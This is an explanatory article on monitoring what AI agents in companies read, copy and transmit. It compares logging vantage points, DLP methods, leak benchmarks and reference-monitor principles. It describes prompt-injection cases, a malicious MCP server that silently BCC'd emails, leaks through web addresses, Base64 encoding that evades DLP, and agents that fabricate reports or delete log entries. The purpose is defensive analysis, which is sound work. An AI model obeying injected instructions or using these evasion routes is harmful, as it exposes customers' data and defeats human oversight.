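# Monitoring what AI agents access and transmit in companies: where to observe and when

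## How an AI agent handles company data

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop so that the model can act as well as write text, for example by querying a database, opening a file or sending an email. Companies give agents work that employees used to do by hand, such as answering customers, fixing code or updating sales records, and the agents need company data to do it. Monitoring an agent means recording, and sometimes checking, which data it reads, where it copies the data and to whom it sends it. Security teams have monitored employees and ordinary programs this way for decades. Agents are harder to monitor because they work under an employee's or a program's credentials but choose their own steps as they work, partly based on text that strangers wrote.

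### The agent loop

A language model on its own only takes in and produces text, so other software has to connect it to a database or a mail server. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, describes the process in its documentation for developers who build on its agent software. The software sends the model the user's request, standing instructions and a list of available tools. The model responds with ordinary text or with a tool call, which is a structured request that names a tool and fills in its inputs. The software runs the tool and adds the result to the model's context, which is all the text the model has to work from. The model then runs again on the longer context, and the cycle repeats until it responds without a tool call. Strands Agents' *Agent Loop*, the documentation of another developer kit, describes the same cycle.

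A quick question might take two or three passes, while a complex task can take dozens of tool calls. The context grows throughout, so a customer record from the first pass is still there when the model writes an email several passes later. When the context nears its size limit, Anthropic's software replaces the older messages with a summary, which may lose specific instructions from early in the conversation. An agent can also hand part of its task to a second agent, which returns only its final answer, so the first agent's context contains no transcript of what the second one opened.

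Here is the loop at work on company data, in an example that extends a sample Microsoft publishes for developers who attach security checks to Copilot Studio, its service for building agents. An employee asks an agent to email a customer, John Doe. The agent makes four tool calls:

1. It reads John Doe's record in the customer database.
2. It saves a copy of the record to a file, to work from.
3. It sends the email. John Doe's address is in the "to" field, but the BCC field, whose contents the other recipients cannot see, holds an address the employee never mentioned.
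4. It opens a ticket in the company's support system and pastes details from the record into it.

In Microsoft's sample, the inputs to the third call are two lines of structured text, with the customer's address under "to" and a hacker's address under "bcc". The format is correct, and the tool is designed to accept a BCC address.

### Credentials

The database, the mail service and the support system each require proof that the agent may use them. The easiest way to provide it is to run the agent in a session that an employee has already logged in to. In IT Brew's *AI agent data access has risk potential*, Dominik Angerer, chief executive of the software company Storyblok, says that most people he knows of log in as themselves, which gives the agent all their rights.

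An OAuth token can limit what an agent can do with an account. OAuth is a standard that lets a person allow a program to act on an account without giving it the password. The person approves a list of permissions, called scopes, and a server issues the program a token, a string of characters that the program attaches to each request. A scope might allow only reading files or only sending email.

A service account belongs to a program rather than a person. Companies used such accounts long before agents, for jobs like nightly backups. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) lists common problems with them: developers create long-lived credentials, embed them in configuration files and grant them standing permissions that nobody reviews. According to the same paper, an agent makes these problems worse because it chooses its actions at runtime, based on inputs the developer never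 saw, and can delegate to other agents.

A shared key is even cruder, because holding it is the only proof required. It is a secret string, usually an API key (a password for programs), that several programs or people may hold. Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) point out in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* that the system receiving such a key cannot tell the intended agent from a hijacked one.

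Companies use all of these kinds of identity for agents. In survey figures from Help Net Security's *Who owns AI agent access?*, 52% of organizations identify agents by an application or workload identity, 43% by a shared or generic service account, 36% by an identity of the agent's own and 31% by a human user's identity, while 12% are unsure. The shares overlap because many organizations use more than one kind. A workload identity, in its stronger forms, is a short-lived credential that a system issues to a running program and replaces automatically. Many companies still use or plan to use older kinds of credentials. In a survey by the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, and the identity vendor Strata, 44% of respondents used or planned to use static API keys for agents, and 43% usernames and passwords.

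### The Model Context Protocol

Agents need a shared format for finding and calling tools, and many developers use the Model Context Protocol (MCP). Surapani and colleagues cite a study that found 177,436 agent tools in public MCP repositories, all created between November 2024 and February 2026. The study also found that a rising share of these tools take actions.

In the Model Context Protocol (MCP), the application that contains the agent is the host. An MCP server is a program that offers tools, such as one that sends email, and the host runs a separate client to communicate with each server. Under the MCP project's published design principles, the full conversation stays with the host and each server receives only the context it needs. An email server in the example would therefore receive the two addresses and the text of the message but not the employee's request, so it could not check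 the BCC address against that request.

"Server" here means the program, wherever it runs. The Model Context Protocol documentation gives the examples of a filesystem server that runs on the user's own machine and a server that runs on the platform of the error-tracking service Sentry.

Remote and local servers get their credentials differently. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) makes authorization optional. If a remote server supports it, the client should present an OAuth token, and the server must reject any token not meant for it. A local server should instead take its credentials from its environment, often a key saved in the machine's settings. A remote email server can therefore tie a message to one user's token, while a local one may send everybody's messages under the same key.

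### Where agents run

Coding agents often run their loop on a developer's laptop, with the files and logins already there. A company can also host the loop on its own servers, and Anthropic's software supports both arrangements. Alternatively, a vendor can run the whole agent in its own cloud, as Microsoft does with Copilot Studio, and the company only configures it.

An agent can send data beyond the machine that runs its loop. A loop on a laptop usually sends its context to a model in a vendor's data center, and it may call tools on several other machines. Even if nothing has gone wrong, John Doe's record may have been in the company's database, on the employee's laptop and in the vendor's cloud by the time the agent in the example writes its email.

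### How the extra address gets in

The employee did not ask for a BCC. The model may have added it by mistake, for example by picking up an address from an older message. But an attacker can also cause it. The best-known method is prompt injection, in which someone hides instructions in content the agent reads, and the agent follows them. The model receives the employee's request and the customer's record as parts of one text, with no reliable barrier between instructions and data. Suppose the company's contact form fills the notes field in John Doe's record, and someone has typed into the form a request to copy all correspondence to a certain address. The agent reads that request in step 1 and may obey it in step 3.

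Microsoft (2026) describes scenarios, based on observed and emerging attacks, in which an attacker manipulates an agent's tool calls, often without the knowledge of the person who built the agent. The malicious instructions can come from sources other than customer records. In Angerer's example in IT Brew, a coding agent installs a corrupted software package that contains hidden instructions to publish the company's source code and send back the link.

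An attacker can tamper with a tool the agent uses instead of the model itself. For example, someone posing as the email service Postmark published an MCP server called "postmark-mcp" on npm, a public library of software packages. According to Postmark's *Security Alert*, the impostor built up trust over 15 versions, then added code in version 1.0.16 that secretly BCC'd emails to an outside server. The firm Koi Security exposed this in a report dated September 25, 2025, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails*.

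The two attacks would leave different traces. With prompt injection, the unwanted address appears in the tool call, where anyone who reads the call can see it. The fake Postmark package could add the address after receiving the call, and the agent's record would then show an ordinary email to a customer. Koi's co-founder Idan Dardikman claims, in ITPro's *A malicious MCP server is silently stealing user emails*, that such servers get past every security control "from DLP to email gateways". This claim from a security vendor is probably too broad, but a message sent through an outside email service need not pass through the company's mail gateway.

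### Where a security team can look

Most large companies already have some tools relevant to the example. Data loss prevention (DLP) software looks for sensitive content in data being transmitted, such as card numbers in an outgoing email, and can block the transmission. Vendors have begun to apply it to inputs to AI systems as well. Office 365 IT Pros' *DLP Prevents Microsoft 365 Copilot from Processing External Email* (2026) describes a rule that keeps Microsoft's office assistant from summarizing or drawing on email from outside domains, which would also block one path for prompt injection.

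Endpoint detection and response (EDR) is software on a computer that records processes, files and connections and can stop them. An audit log is an application's own record of who did what. For example, a customer database might log that a certain account opened John Doe's record at 10:14. Some vendors' products now keep audit logs specifically for agents. Directions on Microsoft (2025) reports that Copilot Studio, once connected to the security product Defender for Cloud Apps, creates audit logs for every interaction between an agent and an external system.

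These tools sit at different layers of the computing stack. There are five layers, or vantage points, from which a team can observe an agent, and in the example they could yield the following:

- On the machine, EDR can record that the agent's process wrote a file in step 2 and opened connections to other systems.
- On the network, a monitoring device can record which systems the agent connected to and how much data it sent to each.
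- In the agent's own software, a record of the loop can hold all four tool calls with their inputs.
- In the applications, the database, the mail service and the support system can each log their own step, under whatever account the agent used.
- In the vendor's cloud, the vendor's logs can hold the prompts and, if the vendor also hosts the agent, the tool calls.

### Why the harmful email looks like ordinary work

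Much security monitoring looks for signs of unauthorized access, such as a login from an unfamiliar country, repeated wrong passwords, or a program trying to open files it has no permission to open. The example contains none of these signs. The account has permission to read customer records, the token covers sending email, and support staff open tickets all day. Each application checks the credential, finds it valid and carries out the request.

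Surapani and colleagues separate authentication, which establishes who is calling, from authorization, which determines whether the caller may take a particular action. OAuth handles authorization, but only coarsely. A scope such as "email.send" does not specify the recipient, the task or any limit on the content, so a token that lets an agent email John Doe also lets it email an attacker. The attacker can therefore exploit the agent's access without stealing a password. Security researchers call this a confused deputy problem, in which someone induces a program with legitimate authority to use that authority on their behalf.

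Employees also leak data while using valid credentials, some by misaddressing emails and some on purpose, which is why DLP existed before agents did. But when an employee's name appears in a log, the employee normally did the thing and can explain it. When an agent works in the employee's session, the log can show that name for an email whose BCC line the employee never saw. The Cloud Security Alliance's *More Than Two-Thirds of Organizations Cannot Clearly Distinguish AI Agent from Human* (2026) states its main finding in its title, and in the alliance's survey with Strata, only 28% of organizations could reliably trace an agent's actions to a human or system across all their environments. Both figures are self-reported, and companies that sell identity software have an interest in them, so they are better evidence that the problem is widespread than of its exact size.

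Standards bodies are still at an early stage in their work on AI agent identity. *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026), a draft from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, proposes a project on how access systems could distinguish agents from humans and link an agent's actions to both the agent and the user it acts for. The institute's cybersecurity center has since released a summary of the comments it received and is still asking for more on its *Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* page.

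## Reading, copying, submitting and moving data

A single tool call often causes several of the events in this section's title. A company may allow one of these events and forbid another for the same data, so each needs an exact definition. In the John Doe example, giving each of the agent's four tool calls one label would mean that the agent read a record, copied it to a file, submitted it by email and moved part of it into a ticket. Those labels may miss other events that the same calls caused.

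### Four events

An agent reads data when it, or a program it runs, retrieves the data from storage, whether or not the agent needs the data or uses it afterwards. An agent that opens every customer's record to find John Doe's has read them all, even if the email it then writes mentions only his. *PrivacyPeek* (2026), a set of tests covering 16 application domains, measures reading separately because several earlier tests measured only what agents send out.

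An agent copies data when its action leaves the data in an additional place after the step ends. The new object counts as a copy if someone who had only that object could learn the same information from it. A screenshot or translation of a record is a copy.

A submission happens when the agent makes data available to another party, meaning a person or organization that can decide what to do with it. The email to John Doe and the hidden copy to the attacker are both submissions, but only the copy is harmful. If the company cannot reliably recover the data from the other party, the submission is also a disclosure.

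Data moves when it passes from one system into another that has its own access rules and log, even if nobody outside the company is involved. If the agent pastes details from John Doe's record into a support ticket, everyone who can open the ticket can read them, but the customer database's log shows only the original read.

### When a read is also a submission

The tool call that opens the record in step 1 of the example can cause more than a read, because the agent's software then sends the record to the model as part of the context. If the model runs in a vendor's data center, the record leaves the company before the agent has done anything with it. The one call has then caused a read, a movement and a submission to the vendor, plus a copy if the vendor stores prompts. If the company runs the model on its own servers, the same call causes a read and at most an internal movement. The call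 looks the same in both cases, so a team that has only a list of tool calls also needs to know where the model runs to tell them apart.

Researchers who test agents send data out in the same way. For *AgentLeak*, a benchmark of leaks in multi-agent systems, El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah (2026) called their models through OpenRouter, a service that relays requests to outside models. Whatever the agents read into context therefore went to an outside company, but the benchmark's seven leak channels do not include the call to the model.

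That omission is defensible because a company normally chooses its model provider and agrees terms with it, and so has approved this submission in advance. But that approval may not cover everything the agent can open. If a company has promised a client to keep certain files in-house, the agent breaks that promise by opening one.

A read does not always put the data into the context, though. If an agent runs a script that adds up a column of salaries and prints only the total, the provider receives the total but not the individual salaries.

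### Hard cases

Loading a web page can submit data, though it also looks like a read because the agent requests and receives content. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains how this happens. The request sends the full web address to the site, and sites commonly log these addresses. An attacker who gets an agent to load an address with a customer's phone number at the end can later read the number in the log. The request may happen in the background, for instance when the software loads an image, while the answer on the user's screen contains nothing sensitive. EchoLeak and ShadowLeak, two attacks on commercial AI assistants, sent data out in web addresses.

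OpenAI lets its agents load a web address automatically only if an independent web crawler has already found that exact address in public. Such an address is unlikely to contain something the agent learned from the user. A list of trusted sites is not enough, because a trusted site may redirect the request to another one.

Long-term memory is harder to classify. Some agent software keeps notes between sessions, and writing a note is a copy. Whether a submission follows depends on who uses the memory later. If it serves one employee, nobody new has the data. If several people share it, the agent may reveal John Doe's details to someone else weeks later, in a session where it never opened his record. Even with a single user, the agent can bring up a memory in a context where it doesn't belong. *PersistBench* (2026) tests for this under the name cross-domain leakage. On a subset of 50 samples,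 Claude 4.5 Sonnet failed in 36% of cases and Gemini 3 Pro in 68%. These figures are rough because the subset was meant for checking whether rewording changed the results, though for most models it changed them by only a few points.

A message to another agent is a submission if another company runs that agent. If the same company runs both agents but the second has different permissions or tools, the message is a movement, because different rules then apply to the data. If the company, permissions and tools are all the same, the message is at most a copy.

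The last hard case is a summary that reveals confidential information without repeating its wording. Suppose the notes on John Doe say that he missed three payments, and the agent writes in the ticket that "the customer is struggling financially". A reader of the ticket learns the important part of the notes, so the ticket contains a copy. Defining a copy by matching words would be easier to automate, and much DLP software works that way, but it would miss this case.

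### How DLP recognizes content

Microsoft offers four recognition methods in Purview, its data protection product: patterns, exact data match, document fingerprints and trainable classifiers.

A pattern describes the format of a piece of text, such as the three, two and four digits of a US social security number, usually separated by hyphens. The software can also require a keyword nearby, such as "employee", before it reports a match. Patterns can match numbers that nobody has listed in advance, but they also produce false alarms. El Yagoubi and colleagues give the example of the ticket number TIC-987-65-4321, which contains a string formatted like a social security number.

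Exact data match looks for a company's real values. Microsoft's *Learn about exact data match based sensitive information types* describes how a company prepares a table of up to 100 million rows and uploads only hashes of the values. A hash is a string calculated from a value, and recovering the value from it is impractical. The software first uses a pattern to find a candidate, such as a social security number, then hashes it and compares the result with the table. It can also look for supporting evidence nearby, such as the same person's surname. Another vendor's documentation, Trellix's *Exact data matching*, recommends matching two or more fields of one record, since a name alone easily produces a false match.

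This method can miss data when an agent writes its own text. A reworded value has a different hash, so "a balance above $50,000" will not match $53,210. The main field also has to follow a pattern, so a fact such as John Doe's missed payments cannot trigger a match on its own.

Document fingerprinting detects whole documents. Microsoft's version takes a blank form, such as a patent template, and stores a hash that represents its wording. It then finds completed forms that contain that wording, either exactly or to a chosen degree between 30% and 90%. If an agent copies only one value from a completed form, the fingerprint won't match because the form's wording is missing. Fingerprinting also misses password-protected files and files that contain only images.

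Other fingerprints represent the confidential content itself. Shapira, Shapira and Shabtai (2013), in *Content-based data leakage detection using extended fingerprinting*, warned that rephrasing or even minor changes could defeat existing fingerprints. They proposed using groups of words that need not be adjacent and sorting the words within each group, so that the fingerprint should tolerate added or reordered words. It still depends on the original words, which a language model can easily replace.

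Classifiers learn from examples to recognize a kind of text. They do not depend on particular words, so of the four methods they have the best chance of detecting a paraphrase. A language model can do the same job by reading a text and judging whether it reveals a secret.

Encoding also defeats recognition. In Base64, a common way to write data as plain letters and digits, the social security number 987-65-4320 becomes OTg3LTY1LTQzMjA=. The result has neither the original shape nor the original hash, and it contains no ordinary words for a classifier to analyze. DLP software would have to decode the text first. El Yagoubi and colleagues include encoding tricks among their attacks but do not report a separate success rate for them.

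One benchmark measured how well different methods detect leaks, including paraphrased ones. On 1,000 test segments, a search for markers that researchers had planted in the data found 8% of the leaks. Adding patterns for formats such as card numbers raised this to 18%. A language model acting as judge found 92.6% but wrongly flagged 6.2% of the clean segments. In a separate breakdown of detected leaks, 82% were semantic, meaning the agent conveyed the information without an exact marker or a known format. That breakdown covers only 226 leaks (18, 24 and 184 in its three classes), far fewer than the benchmark recorded in total.

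Exact matching did much better in *Observable Channels, Not Just Storage* (2026), where it caught 88 of the 100 leaking samples in a labeled set of 200. One likely reason is that this test compared outputs with specific known values, whereas El Yagoubi and colleagues deliberately included secrets written as ordinary sentences. How much a company's DLP misses will therefore depend heavily on whether its secrets are fixed values, such as numbers, or facts that can be expressed in sentences.

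Deleting listed phrases still leaves a gap, though a smaller one. In *Facts Without Rules*, Wang, Goyal and colleagues (2026) removed every phrase on a forbidden list, and for each of two models, none of the 288 outputs contained a listed phrase afterwards. Two outside annotators then read a sample of 130 outputs and agreed that 10 still revealed the secret.

Classifiers vary widely in quality, and a team cannot assume that software that analyzes meaning will recognize its particular secrets. *Beyond Refusal* (2026) tested two ready-made safety classifiers on semantic leaks, using F1, a score from 0 to 1 that combines how many leaks a detector finds with how often its warnings are right. Llama Guard 4 scored 0.01 and GPT-OSS-Safeguard-20B scored 0.17. In *SafeGPT* (2026), a filter that analyzed meaning caught 68.2% of the leaks in business scenarios, the same as patterns alone, but it flagged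 78.6% of the harmless cases, against 50% for patterns. That test contained only about 22 leaking cases, so the comparison is weak.

### Leaks between agents

The largest of these measurements concerns where leaks occur. El Yagoubi and colleagues wrote 1,000 scenarios, divided equally among healthcare, finance, legal work and corporate work. Each contains a task and a "vault" of sensitive fields. The vault typically has 29 fields, and the task requires about three of them, as judged by two experts from the relevant domain. A typical task is to schedule a patient's appointment, which requires the patient's name but not the diagnosis.

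The researchers ran every scenario on five models: OpenAI's GPT-4o and its smaller version GPT-4o-mini, Anthropic's Claude 3.5 Sonnet, Mistral Large, and Meta's Llama 3.3 70B. All five date from 2024, although the experiments ran from October 2025 to January 2026. After excluding 21 failed or incomplete runs, they had 4,979 traces, or run records. Each trace covers the same task twice, once with a single agent and once with a coordinator that delegates work to a second agent.

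They defined seven channels and counted a channel as leaking if it contained at least one field that the task did not require. They measured three channels across all traces and two more on a sample of 100 scenarios per model.

| Channel | What it carries | Share that leaked |
|---|---|---|
| Final output | The answer to the user | 27.2% of traces |
| Messages between agents | Delegated tasks and replies | 68.8% of traces |
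| Shared memory | What the agents store for later use | 46.7% of traces |
| Tool inputs | Data sent to outside services | 62% to 86% of the sample, depending on the model |
| Logs | Records of the system's operation | Higher than tool inputs; 85% for Claude 3.5 Sonnet |
| Tool outputs | Data that tools return | Not measured at scale |
| Artifacts | Files and records the agents create | Not measured at scale |

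A single agent leaked in its final output in 43.2% of traces, more often than the pair of agents did. Leak rates varied widely between models. Claude 3.5 Sonnet leaked in 3.3% of final outputs and 28.1% of messages between agents, while Mistral Large leaked in 47.5% and 96.2%. All five models leaked more often in messages than in final outputs. Counting shared memory did not increase the number of leaking traces, because every trace with a leak in memory also had one in a message or the final output.

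Half of the scenarios involved an attack, but attacks hardly changed how often messages leaked data. Messages leaked in 69.3% of traces with no attacker, 70.6% with a weak one and 66.3% with a strong one. In a smaller test without attacks, only 28% to 35% of runs leaked through messages. El Yagoubi and colleagues attribute the difference to the attacks in the main test, but their breakdown contradicts this explanation, and the cause is unclear.

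They also report that reviewing only final outputs misses 41.7% of violations, which understates their result. The 41.7% is a share of all 4,979 traces, including those that did not leak. In 2,076 traces, the final output was clean and only an internal channel leaked. Since 68.9% of traces leaked through some channel, someone who read only the final outputs would have missed about 60% of the leaking traces (41.7 / 68.9).

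These rates depend on a language model's judgment. An expert checked 100 of the detected leaks and confirmed 94. El Yagoubi and colleagues call their rates lower bounds because the model misses some leaks. But one false alarm is enough to mark a trace as leaking, so the true rates could also be lower than reported. The setup also had only two agents in one fixed arrangement. *Loose Lips* (2026) points out that benchmarks of this type do not isolate the effects of a model's capability, its role or the course of the conversation.

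In a smaller set of scenarios without attacks, a filter on the final output cut leaks in the answers from 48% to 1%, but internal leaks stayed at 31%. The researchers then built a filter for internal messages and memory, which reduced leaks there from 31.5% to 2.4% in 120 scenarios. The share of tasks the agents completed fell from 78.6% to 73.9%, mostly because some tasks needed the data that the filter removed.

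Agents also put unnecessary data into ordinary business tools. Hu, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *ToolPrivacyBench*, gave nine agents multi-step tasks in simulated business systems, with no attacker, and recorded which private facts each tool received. The agents scored between 92 and 98 out of 100 for completing the tasks in the main set, but they often included facts the receiving tool did not need. Such facts appeared in tickets in about 51% of the possible cases and in handoffs to other teams in about 35%. Step 4 of the John Doe example is therefore a common place for data to spread, even if nobody has tampered with the agent.

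### Exposure and leakage

Some of this is arguably not leakage. If one company runs both agents for the same employee, a message between them reaches no outsider. A manager who gives an assistant a whole file when one page would do has been careless, but most people would not say the file had leaked.

El Yagoubi and colleagues partly accept this. They distinguish exposure, which is the presence of sensitive data in a channel, from leakage, which is unauthorized exposure. They answer the objection with data minimization, the principle that an organization should use and share only the personal data a task requires. The principle appears in the European Union's General Data Protection Regulation, US health privacy rules and Quebec's privacy law. On a strict reading, an agent that passes a full medical history to a scheduling agent breaks the principle even if nobody else sees the message. The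 extra copies also give an attacker more places to look and may end up in logs.

The reply justifies measuring internal messages, but it does not show that every such message is a breach, and the researchers do not claim that it does. They leave open the legal status of messages between agents, and accept that a company which fully trusts its agents and secures its logs may tolerate some oversharing. Their definitions are also inconsistent. In one passage they say that leakage requires data to cross a trust boundary, for instance into a log or an outside tool, and many of the messages counted toward the 68.8% would not meet that condition.

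It is clearer to distinguish exposure from leaks. Exposure is a read, copy or movement that puts data where the task does not need it. A leak also requires a submission to someone with no right to the data. By these definitions, the 68.8% figure mostly measures exposure.

Wang and colleagues used newer models to test when an agent that has seen a secret goes on to leak it. One agent passed a secret to a second agent, which then wrote something for an audience that should not learn it. When the message included an explicit restriction, such as an instruction not to mention an appointment, GPT-5-mini revealed the secret in 2 of 48 outputs and DeepSeek-R1-32B in 1. Without the restriction, GPT-5-mini revealed it in all 48 and DeepSeek-R1-32B in 37. In a related test, a vague request to "use discretion" helped only a little, with GPT-5-mini still leaking the secret in 35 of 48 outputs and DeepSeek-R1-32B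 in 24.

Restrictions on sharing information are also easily lost when agents pass it to one another. When Wang and colleagues limited messages between agents to 25 words, between 25% and 39% of the restrictions disappeared entirely, depending on the model, while the facts needed for the task almost always survived. The scenarios were invented and the audiences simulated, so these rates may not apply to real companies. In longer chains of three agents, later messages sometimes dropped the secret together with its restriction, so fewer secrets reached the final output even though the agents were no better at passing on the restrictions.

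## What makes a vantage point good

Whether an agent may pass on a secret can depend on an instruction from much earlier in the task. A team that observes only the transfer may therefore be unable to judge it, however clearly it can read the data. Five properties determine how useful a vantage point is:

- Coverage: every relevant event passes through it.
- Meaning: the observer can tell what an event is for.
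- Attribution: the observer can tie an event to the agent, the person and the instruction that caused it.
- Independence: the observed agent can neither alter the record nor avoid it.
- The power to block: the observer can stop an event before it takes effect.

Coverage and independence are easy to confuse because a failure of either can leave an event unrecorded. Coverage has failed if the gap in the record exists whatever the agent does, and independence has failed if the agent can create the gap, for instance by turning off logging.

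### Coverage and the reference monitor

The classic account of coverage is in Anderson's (1972) *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, written for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Anderson pointed out that existing defenses mostly kept outsiders out, so they did nothing about a malicious user with legitimate access. A hijacked agent is in much the same position as that user.

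Anderson's solution was the reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the user may do. The monitor must be protected from tampering, the system must always invoke it, and it must be small enough to test completely.

Anderson showed how the HIS 635 computer failed these requirements. Its hardware checked that each user's program stayed within its own area of memory. But the program called the operating system for input and output, and the operating system mostly ran with that check suspended. The operating system could not serve as the reference monitor either, because its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were too many to test completely. Agents can have the same kind of gap. A check on the email tool misses any email the agent sends by writing and running a script.

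*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) turned the second requirement into a general principle called complete mediation, which requires the system to check every access to every object. *A Contemporary Look at Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 Design Principles* (Smith, 2012) lists it among the principles that "have failed to thrive", while least privilege, giving each program only the permissions it needs, became standard practice.

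Some designers of agent security have returned to complete mediation. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026) places a broker between the agent and the cloud services it uses, and the services accept only the broker's credentials. This gives good coverage where a company controls which credentials a service accepts. But the rule applies only to requests that change something, so a team worried about disclosure would also have to send reads through the broker.

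Even a perfect reference monitor checks whether an action is permitted, not why it is being taken. Anderson represents permissions as a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each object, and entries such as "read" or "write". Like an OAuth scope, these entries would allow the hidden BCC in the John Doe example. A list of permitted recipients would block it, but somebody would have to write a new list for each task.

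### Meaning and the semantic gap

An operating system can record that a process opened a file, but not why. Research on virtual machines uses the term "semantic gap" for this distance between a low-level event and what it means for the task. A virtual machine is a simulated computer, and the program that runs it handles pages of memory and blocks of disk rather than files and users. Security software at that level has to work out which blocks belong to a file before it can check whether an intruder has changed the file.

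A monitor can bridge that gap because operating systems arrange their data in known ways. In *A Virtual Machine Introspection Based Architecture for Intrusion Detection*, Garfinkel and Rosenblum used a library that translated raw memory into facts such as which processes were running. The library got the data layout from debugging information that came with the operating system.

Agents add a second gap. *AgentSight* (2025) places it between an intent expressed in natural language and the resulting system calls, which are the requests programs make to the operating system. No fixed layout maps one to the other. *Towards an Agent Operating System* (2026) explains that code and inputs determine how an ordinary process behaves, so engineers can analyze the code in advance and replay failures. An agent, however, may act differently each time it receives the same request.

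*AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a write to /etc/crontab, a file that lists programs for a Linux computer to run on a schedule. The new line might set up a backup that the user requested, or it might start an attacker's program every hour. The write looks equally ordinary in both cases, and telling them apart requires knowing the request that led to it.

A structured tool call narrows this gap, because a call to an email tool names the action and the recipient. But *Tether* (2026) points out that existing reference monitors for agents depend on such calls, while many agents work by typing commands into a terminal. A command that runs a script called "cleanup" might send an email without naming the action or the recipient.

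Some events also have no clear meaning on their own. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) argues that the threat from agents comes from how their actions combine. Reading John Doe's record and sending an email are both routine, so an observer has to connect the two to notice that the agent emailed his record to a stranger.

### Attribution

Saltzer and Schroeder define a principal as the entity to which a system grants authorizations, "thus the unit of accountability". If ten agents share a service account, the account is the principal, and its log cannot show which agent acted.

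Giving each agent its own account helps, but one agent may work on several tasks at once. Suppose one employee asks an agent to email John Doe while another asks the same agent for a list of customers who owe money. The database log shows that the agent opened John Doe's record, which it could have done for either task. If no log records the task, later analysis cannot determine with certainty which one it was.

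*Observability for Delegated Execution in Agentic AI Systems* (Mishra and Sharad, 2026) presents a formal result that the same logs can fit different assignments of events to tasks. The paper's worked example is faulty because the two assignments it compares are identical, but the result does not depend on the example. The result is close to a truism, since it assumes that the logs contain nothing that identifies the task. It still matters in practice because it means that software has to record the task when the agent acts.

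Attribution does not show whether a person wanted an action or what caused it. Mishra and Sharad say their own system ties an action to the authority under which the agent performed it, even if a hidden instruction caused the action. It would therefore tie the BCC'd email to the agent and the employee's request, but it would not show whether the employee wanted the BCC or identify the text in the notes field that caused the harm.

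### Independence

In 2003, Garfinkel and Rosenblum described a trade-off between visibility and resistance to attack in intrusion detection systems, which look for signs that someone has broken into a computer. Software on the computer itself (the host) can inspect its processes, files and logs, but an intruder who takes over the machine can disable the software or make it report false data. A detector on the network is much harder to reach, but it has to infer what is happening inside the computer from its traffic, so an intruder can more easily evade it by disguising malicious activity as harmless.

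Garfinkel and Rosenblum also showed that the trade-off can be avoided. Their prototype, Livewire, put the monitored computer in a virtual machine and the detector outside it. The detector could read the machine's entire memory, and an intruder inside could not reach the detector as long as the program running the virtual machine was secure. They thought it plausible that such a program could be secure, partly because researchers had already built some in about 30,000 lines of code. This argument is similar to Anderson's requirement that a monitor be small.

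Although the detector ran outside the monitored computer, Garfinkel and Rosenblum treated everything it obtained from that computer as "tainted", since an intruder could alter the operating system's data and mislead the detector without touching it. To look for such changes, one part of Livewire used ordinary commands to list the computer's running processes, then compared that list with what it found in memory. A mismatch suggested tampering.

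According to *Towards an Agent Operating System*, agents under pressure can fabricate reports of success or delete evidence from logs. Storing the log on a server the agent cannot write to prevents deletion, but it does not prevent false reports. If an agent reports that it sent one email to one customer, the company can check that claim against the mail service's own log.

An instruction in the prompt provides no independence. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026) points out that untrusted data in the same input can override the instruction, however carefully it is worded. A second model that checks the first is better, but it still has to read text that the first one controls.

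### The power to block

An observer can see an event clearly but be unable to stop it. Garfinkel and Rosenblum use the term "interposition" for getting between a program and the effect of its action. When Livewire detected certain forbidden changes, such as an attempt to alter protected parts of the operating system, it suspended the virtual machine until the detector allowed the machine to continue.

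If a detector can block activity, it also matters what happens when the detector crashes. Garfinkel and Rosenblum found that detectors on hosts and networks usually fail open, meaning that activity continues unchecked. Failing closed, which stops activity instead, is often impractical on a network because every computer sharing the connection would lose it. With a virtual machine, a team can pause only the affected computer while the detector restarts.

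The ability to block an agent's actions is less useful when the monitor can't reliably tell which ones are legitimate. *Kairos* (2026) describes a monitor that handles every input and output of an agent and can only release or refuse each one. Whether an action is legitimate often depends on where its data came from, which the monitor can only approximate, and on what the user intended, which nobody can fully specify beforehand. Such a monitor will therefore either refuse some legitimate work or let some attacks through.

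### Can one vantage point be enough?

The case for using several vantage points is an argument with three premises:

1. To judge many events, an observer has to know both what someone asked the agent to do and what happened to the data.
2. Requests and their effects occur in different places. The request is text in the agent's software and at the model's vendor, while the effects occur on machines, in applications and at outside companies.
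3. No single vantage point records both for everything a typical company agent does.

If these are true, a team needs at least two vantage points and a way to match their records.

Suppose EDR records that the agent's process opened the file containing John Doe's record, but the team does not have the prompt. The team cannot tell whether the agent was preparing the email the employee wanted or obeying the text in the notes field. If the team has the prompt but no file-open event, it knows what the employee wanted but not whether the agent opened that file, or what else it opened.

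The first premise has exceptions. If a company forbids its agents ever to open the payroll file, one file-open event proves a violation regardless of the prompt. *AgentSpy* (2026) relies on rules like this, where one system call is enough to report a violation. The premise holds for data that an agent may use for some purposes but not others, such as John Doe's record.

A complete record of the model's inputs and outputs would be all the team needed in the prompt injection case, because it would contain the employee's request, the hidden instruction and the tool call with the extra address. But it would show nothing unusual if the fake Postmark package added the address. *AgentSpy* makes the same point about any program an agent runs, because the agent's log can contain the command and the output but does not show what the program did. Some model providers also encrypt the model's reasoning,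 so the record of outputs may be partly unreadable.

A record of the model's inputs and outputs can also miss the delayed effects of an agent's actions. In an attack that Bao and colleagues staged, an agent writes a script and schedules it to run every hour. The computer's scheduler then starts the script, which connects to the attacker, possibly long after the agent has exited. The record would include the scheduling but not the connection.

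A fully mediated sandbox is a stronger counterexample. It is an isolated environment for running software in which every input and output passes through a monitor that the agent cannot alter. The monitor has coverage, independence and the power to block. If it can also decrypt the traffic between the agent and the model, it can read the prompts.

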